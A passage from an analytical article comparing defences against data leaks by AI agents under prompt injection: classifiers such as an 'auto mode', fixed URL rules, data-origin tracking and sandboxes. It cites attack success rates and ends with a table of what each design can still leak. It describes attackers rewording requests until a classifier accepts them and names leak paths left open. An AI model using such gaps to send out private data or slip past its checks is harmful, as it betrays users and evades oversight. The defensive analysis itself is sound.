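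Critics object that a classifier replaces a fixed rule with a probabilistic judgement. An attacker can keep rewording a request until a classifier accepts it, but an allowlist that excludes `attacker.example` blocks that address every time. Kolluri and colleagues cite a study in which attackers defeated a combination of two probabilistic defences every time, and 12 others with similar ease. Anthropic reports that in one benchmark about 0.1% of single attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded, but 5–6% did when attackers could adapt over 100 attempts.

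Willison quotes Cat Wu of Anthropic as saying "we've pretty much mitigated every attack". But in its post on containment, Anthropic writes that any probabilistic defence will sometimes miss, and it still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

Defenders of classifiers can reply that a tired user is probably an even less reliable judge. Auto mode caught far more of the planted commands than the testers did, and the testers had refused only six of the 116 it allowed. Asking them to check everything the classifier approved would therefore have caught about 5% of its mistakes, but brought back nearly all the prompts.

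A careful user might do much better than those testers. Anthropic acknowledged in March that auto mode is "arguably a regression" for someone who reviews every action carefully. The company's evidence from real use is also weaker than the experiment, because users chose their own mode and people doing riskier work may have chosen differently. Among sessions that its safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained a serious harmful action the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% in auto mode.

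The reply about tired users supports replacing a prompt with a classifier, but not replacing a fixed rule with one. If a vendor that refuses every constructed URL starts letting a classifier approve some of them, more tasks will work, but some leaks that the old rule would have stopped will get through. If the vendor already asks users about those URLs, a classifier will probably stop more leaks than the users do.

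A vendor can also use fixed rules for the clear cases and a classifier for the rest. The rules can have gaps, as the Cowork upload showed, but the vendor can find and close them. It can lower the classifier's miss rate but can't predict which leaks will get through.

### The designs against the three tasks

The entries for templates and for sessions without private data follow from how those designs work, since neither has published tests.

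| Design | Following links on a page | Search and booking addresses | API calls with parameters | What can still leak |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| URL templates | Only numbered pages, if the template has a page slot | Yes, on sites with a template, unless the search needs free text | Yes, for simple lookups | What the slots can carry, to the template's site |
| Data-origin tracking | Yes, if the plan fixes which link to open | Yes, if the user typed the values and named the site | Yes, on the same conditions | What the agent's choices reveal, unless the software tracks those too |
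| Session without private data | Yes, on public pages | Yes, if no login is needed | Yes, if no private key is needed | The brief |
| Sandbox with network limits | Only on permitted hosts | Only on permitted hosts | Yes, on permitted hosts, including long lists | Any data in the sandbox, through a permitted host that accepts it |
| Classifier | Usually | Usually | Usually | Whatever the classifier misses, including choices between harmless-looking links |
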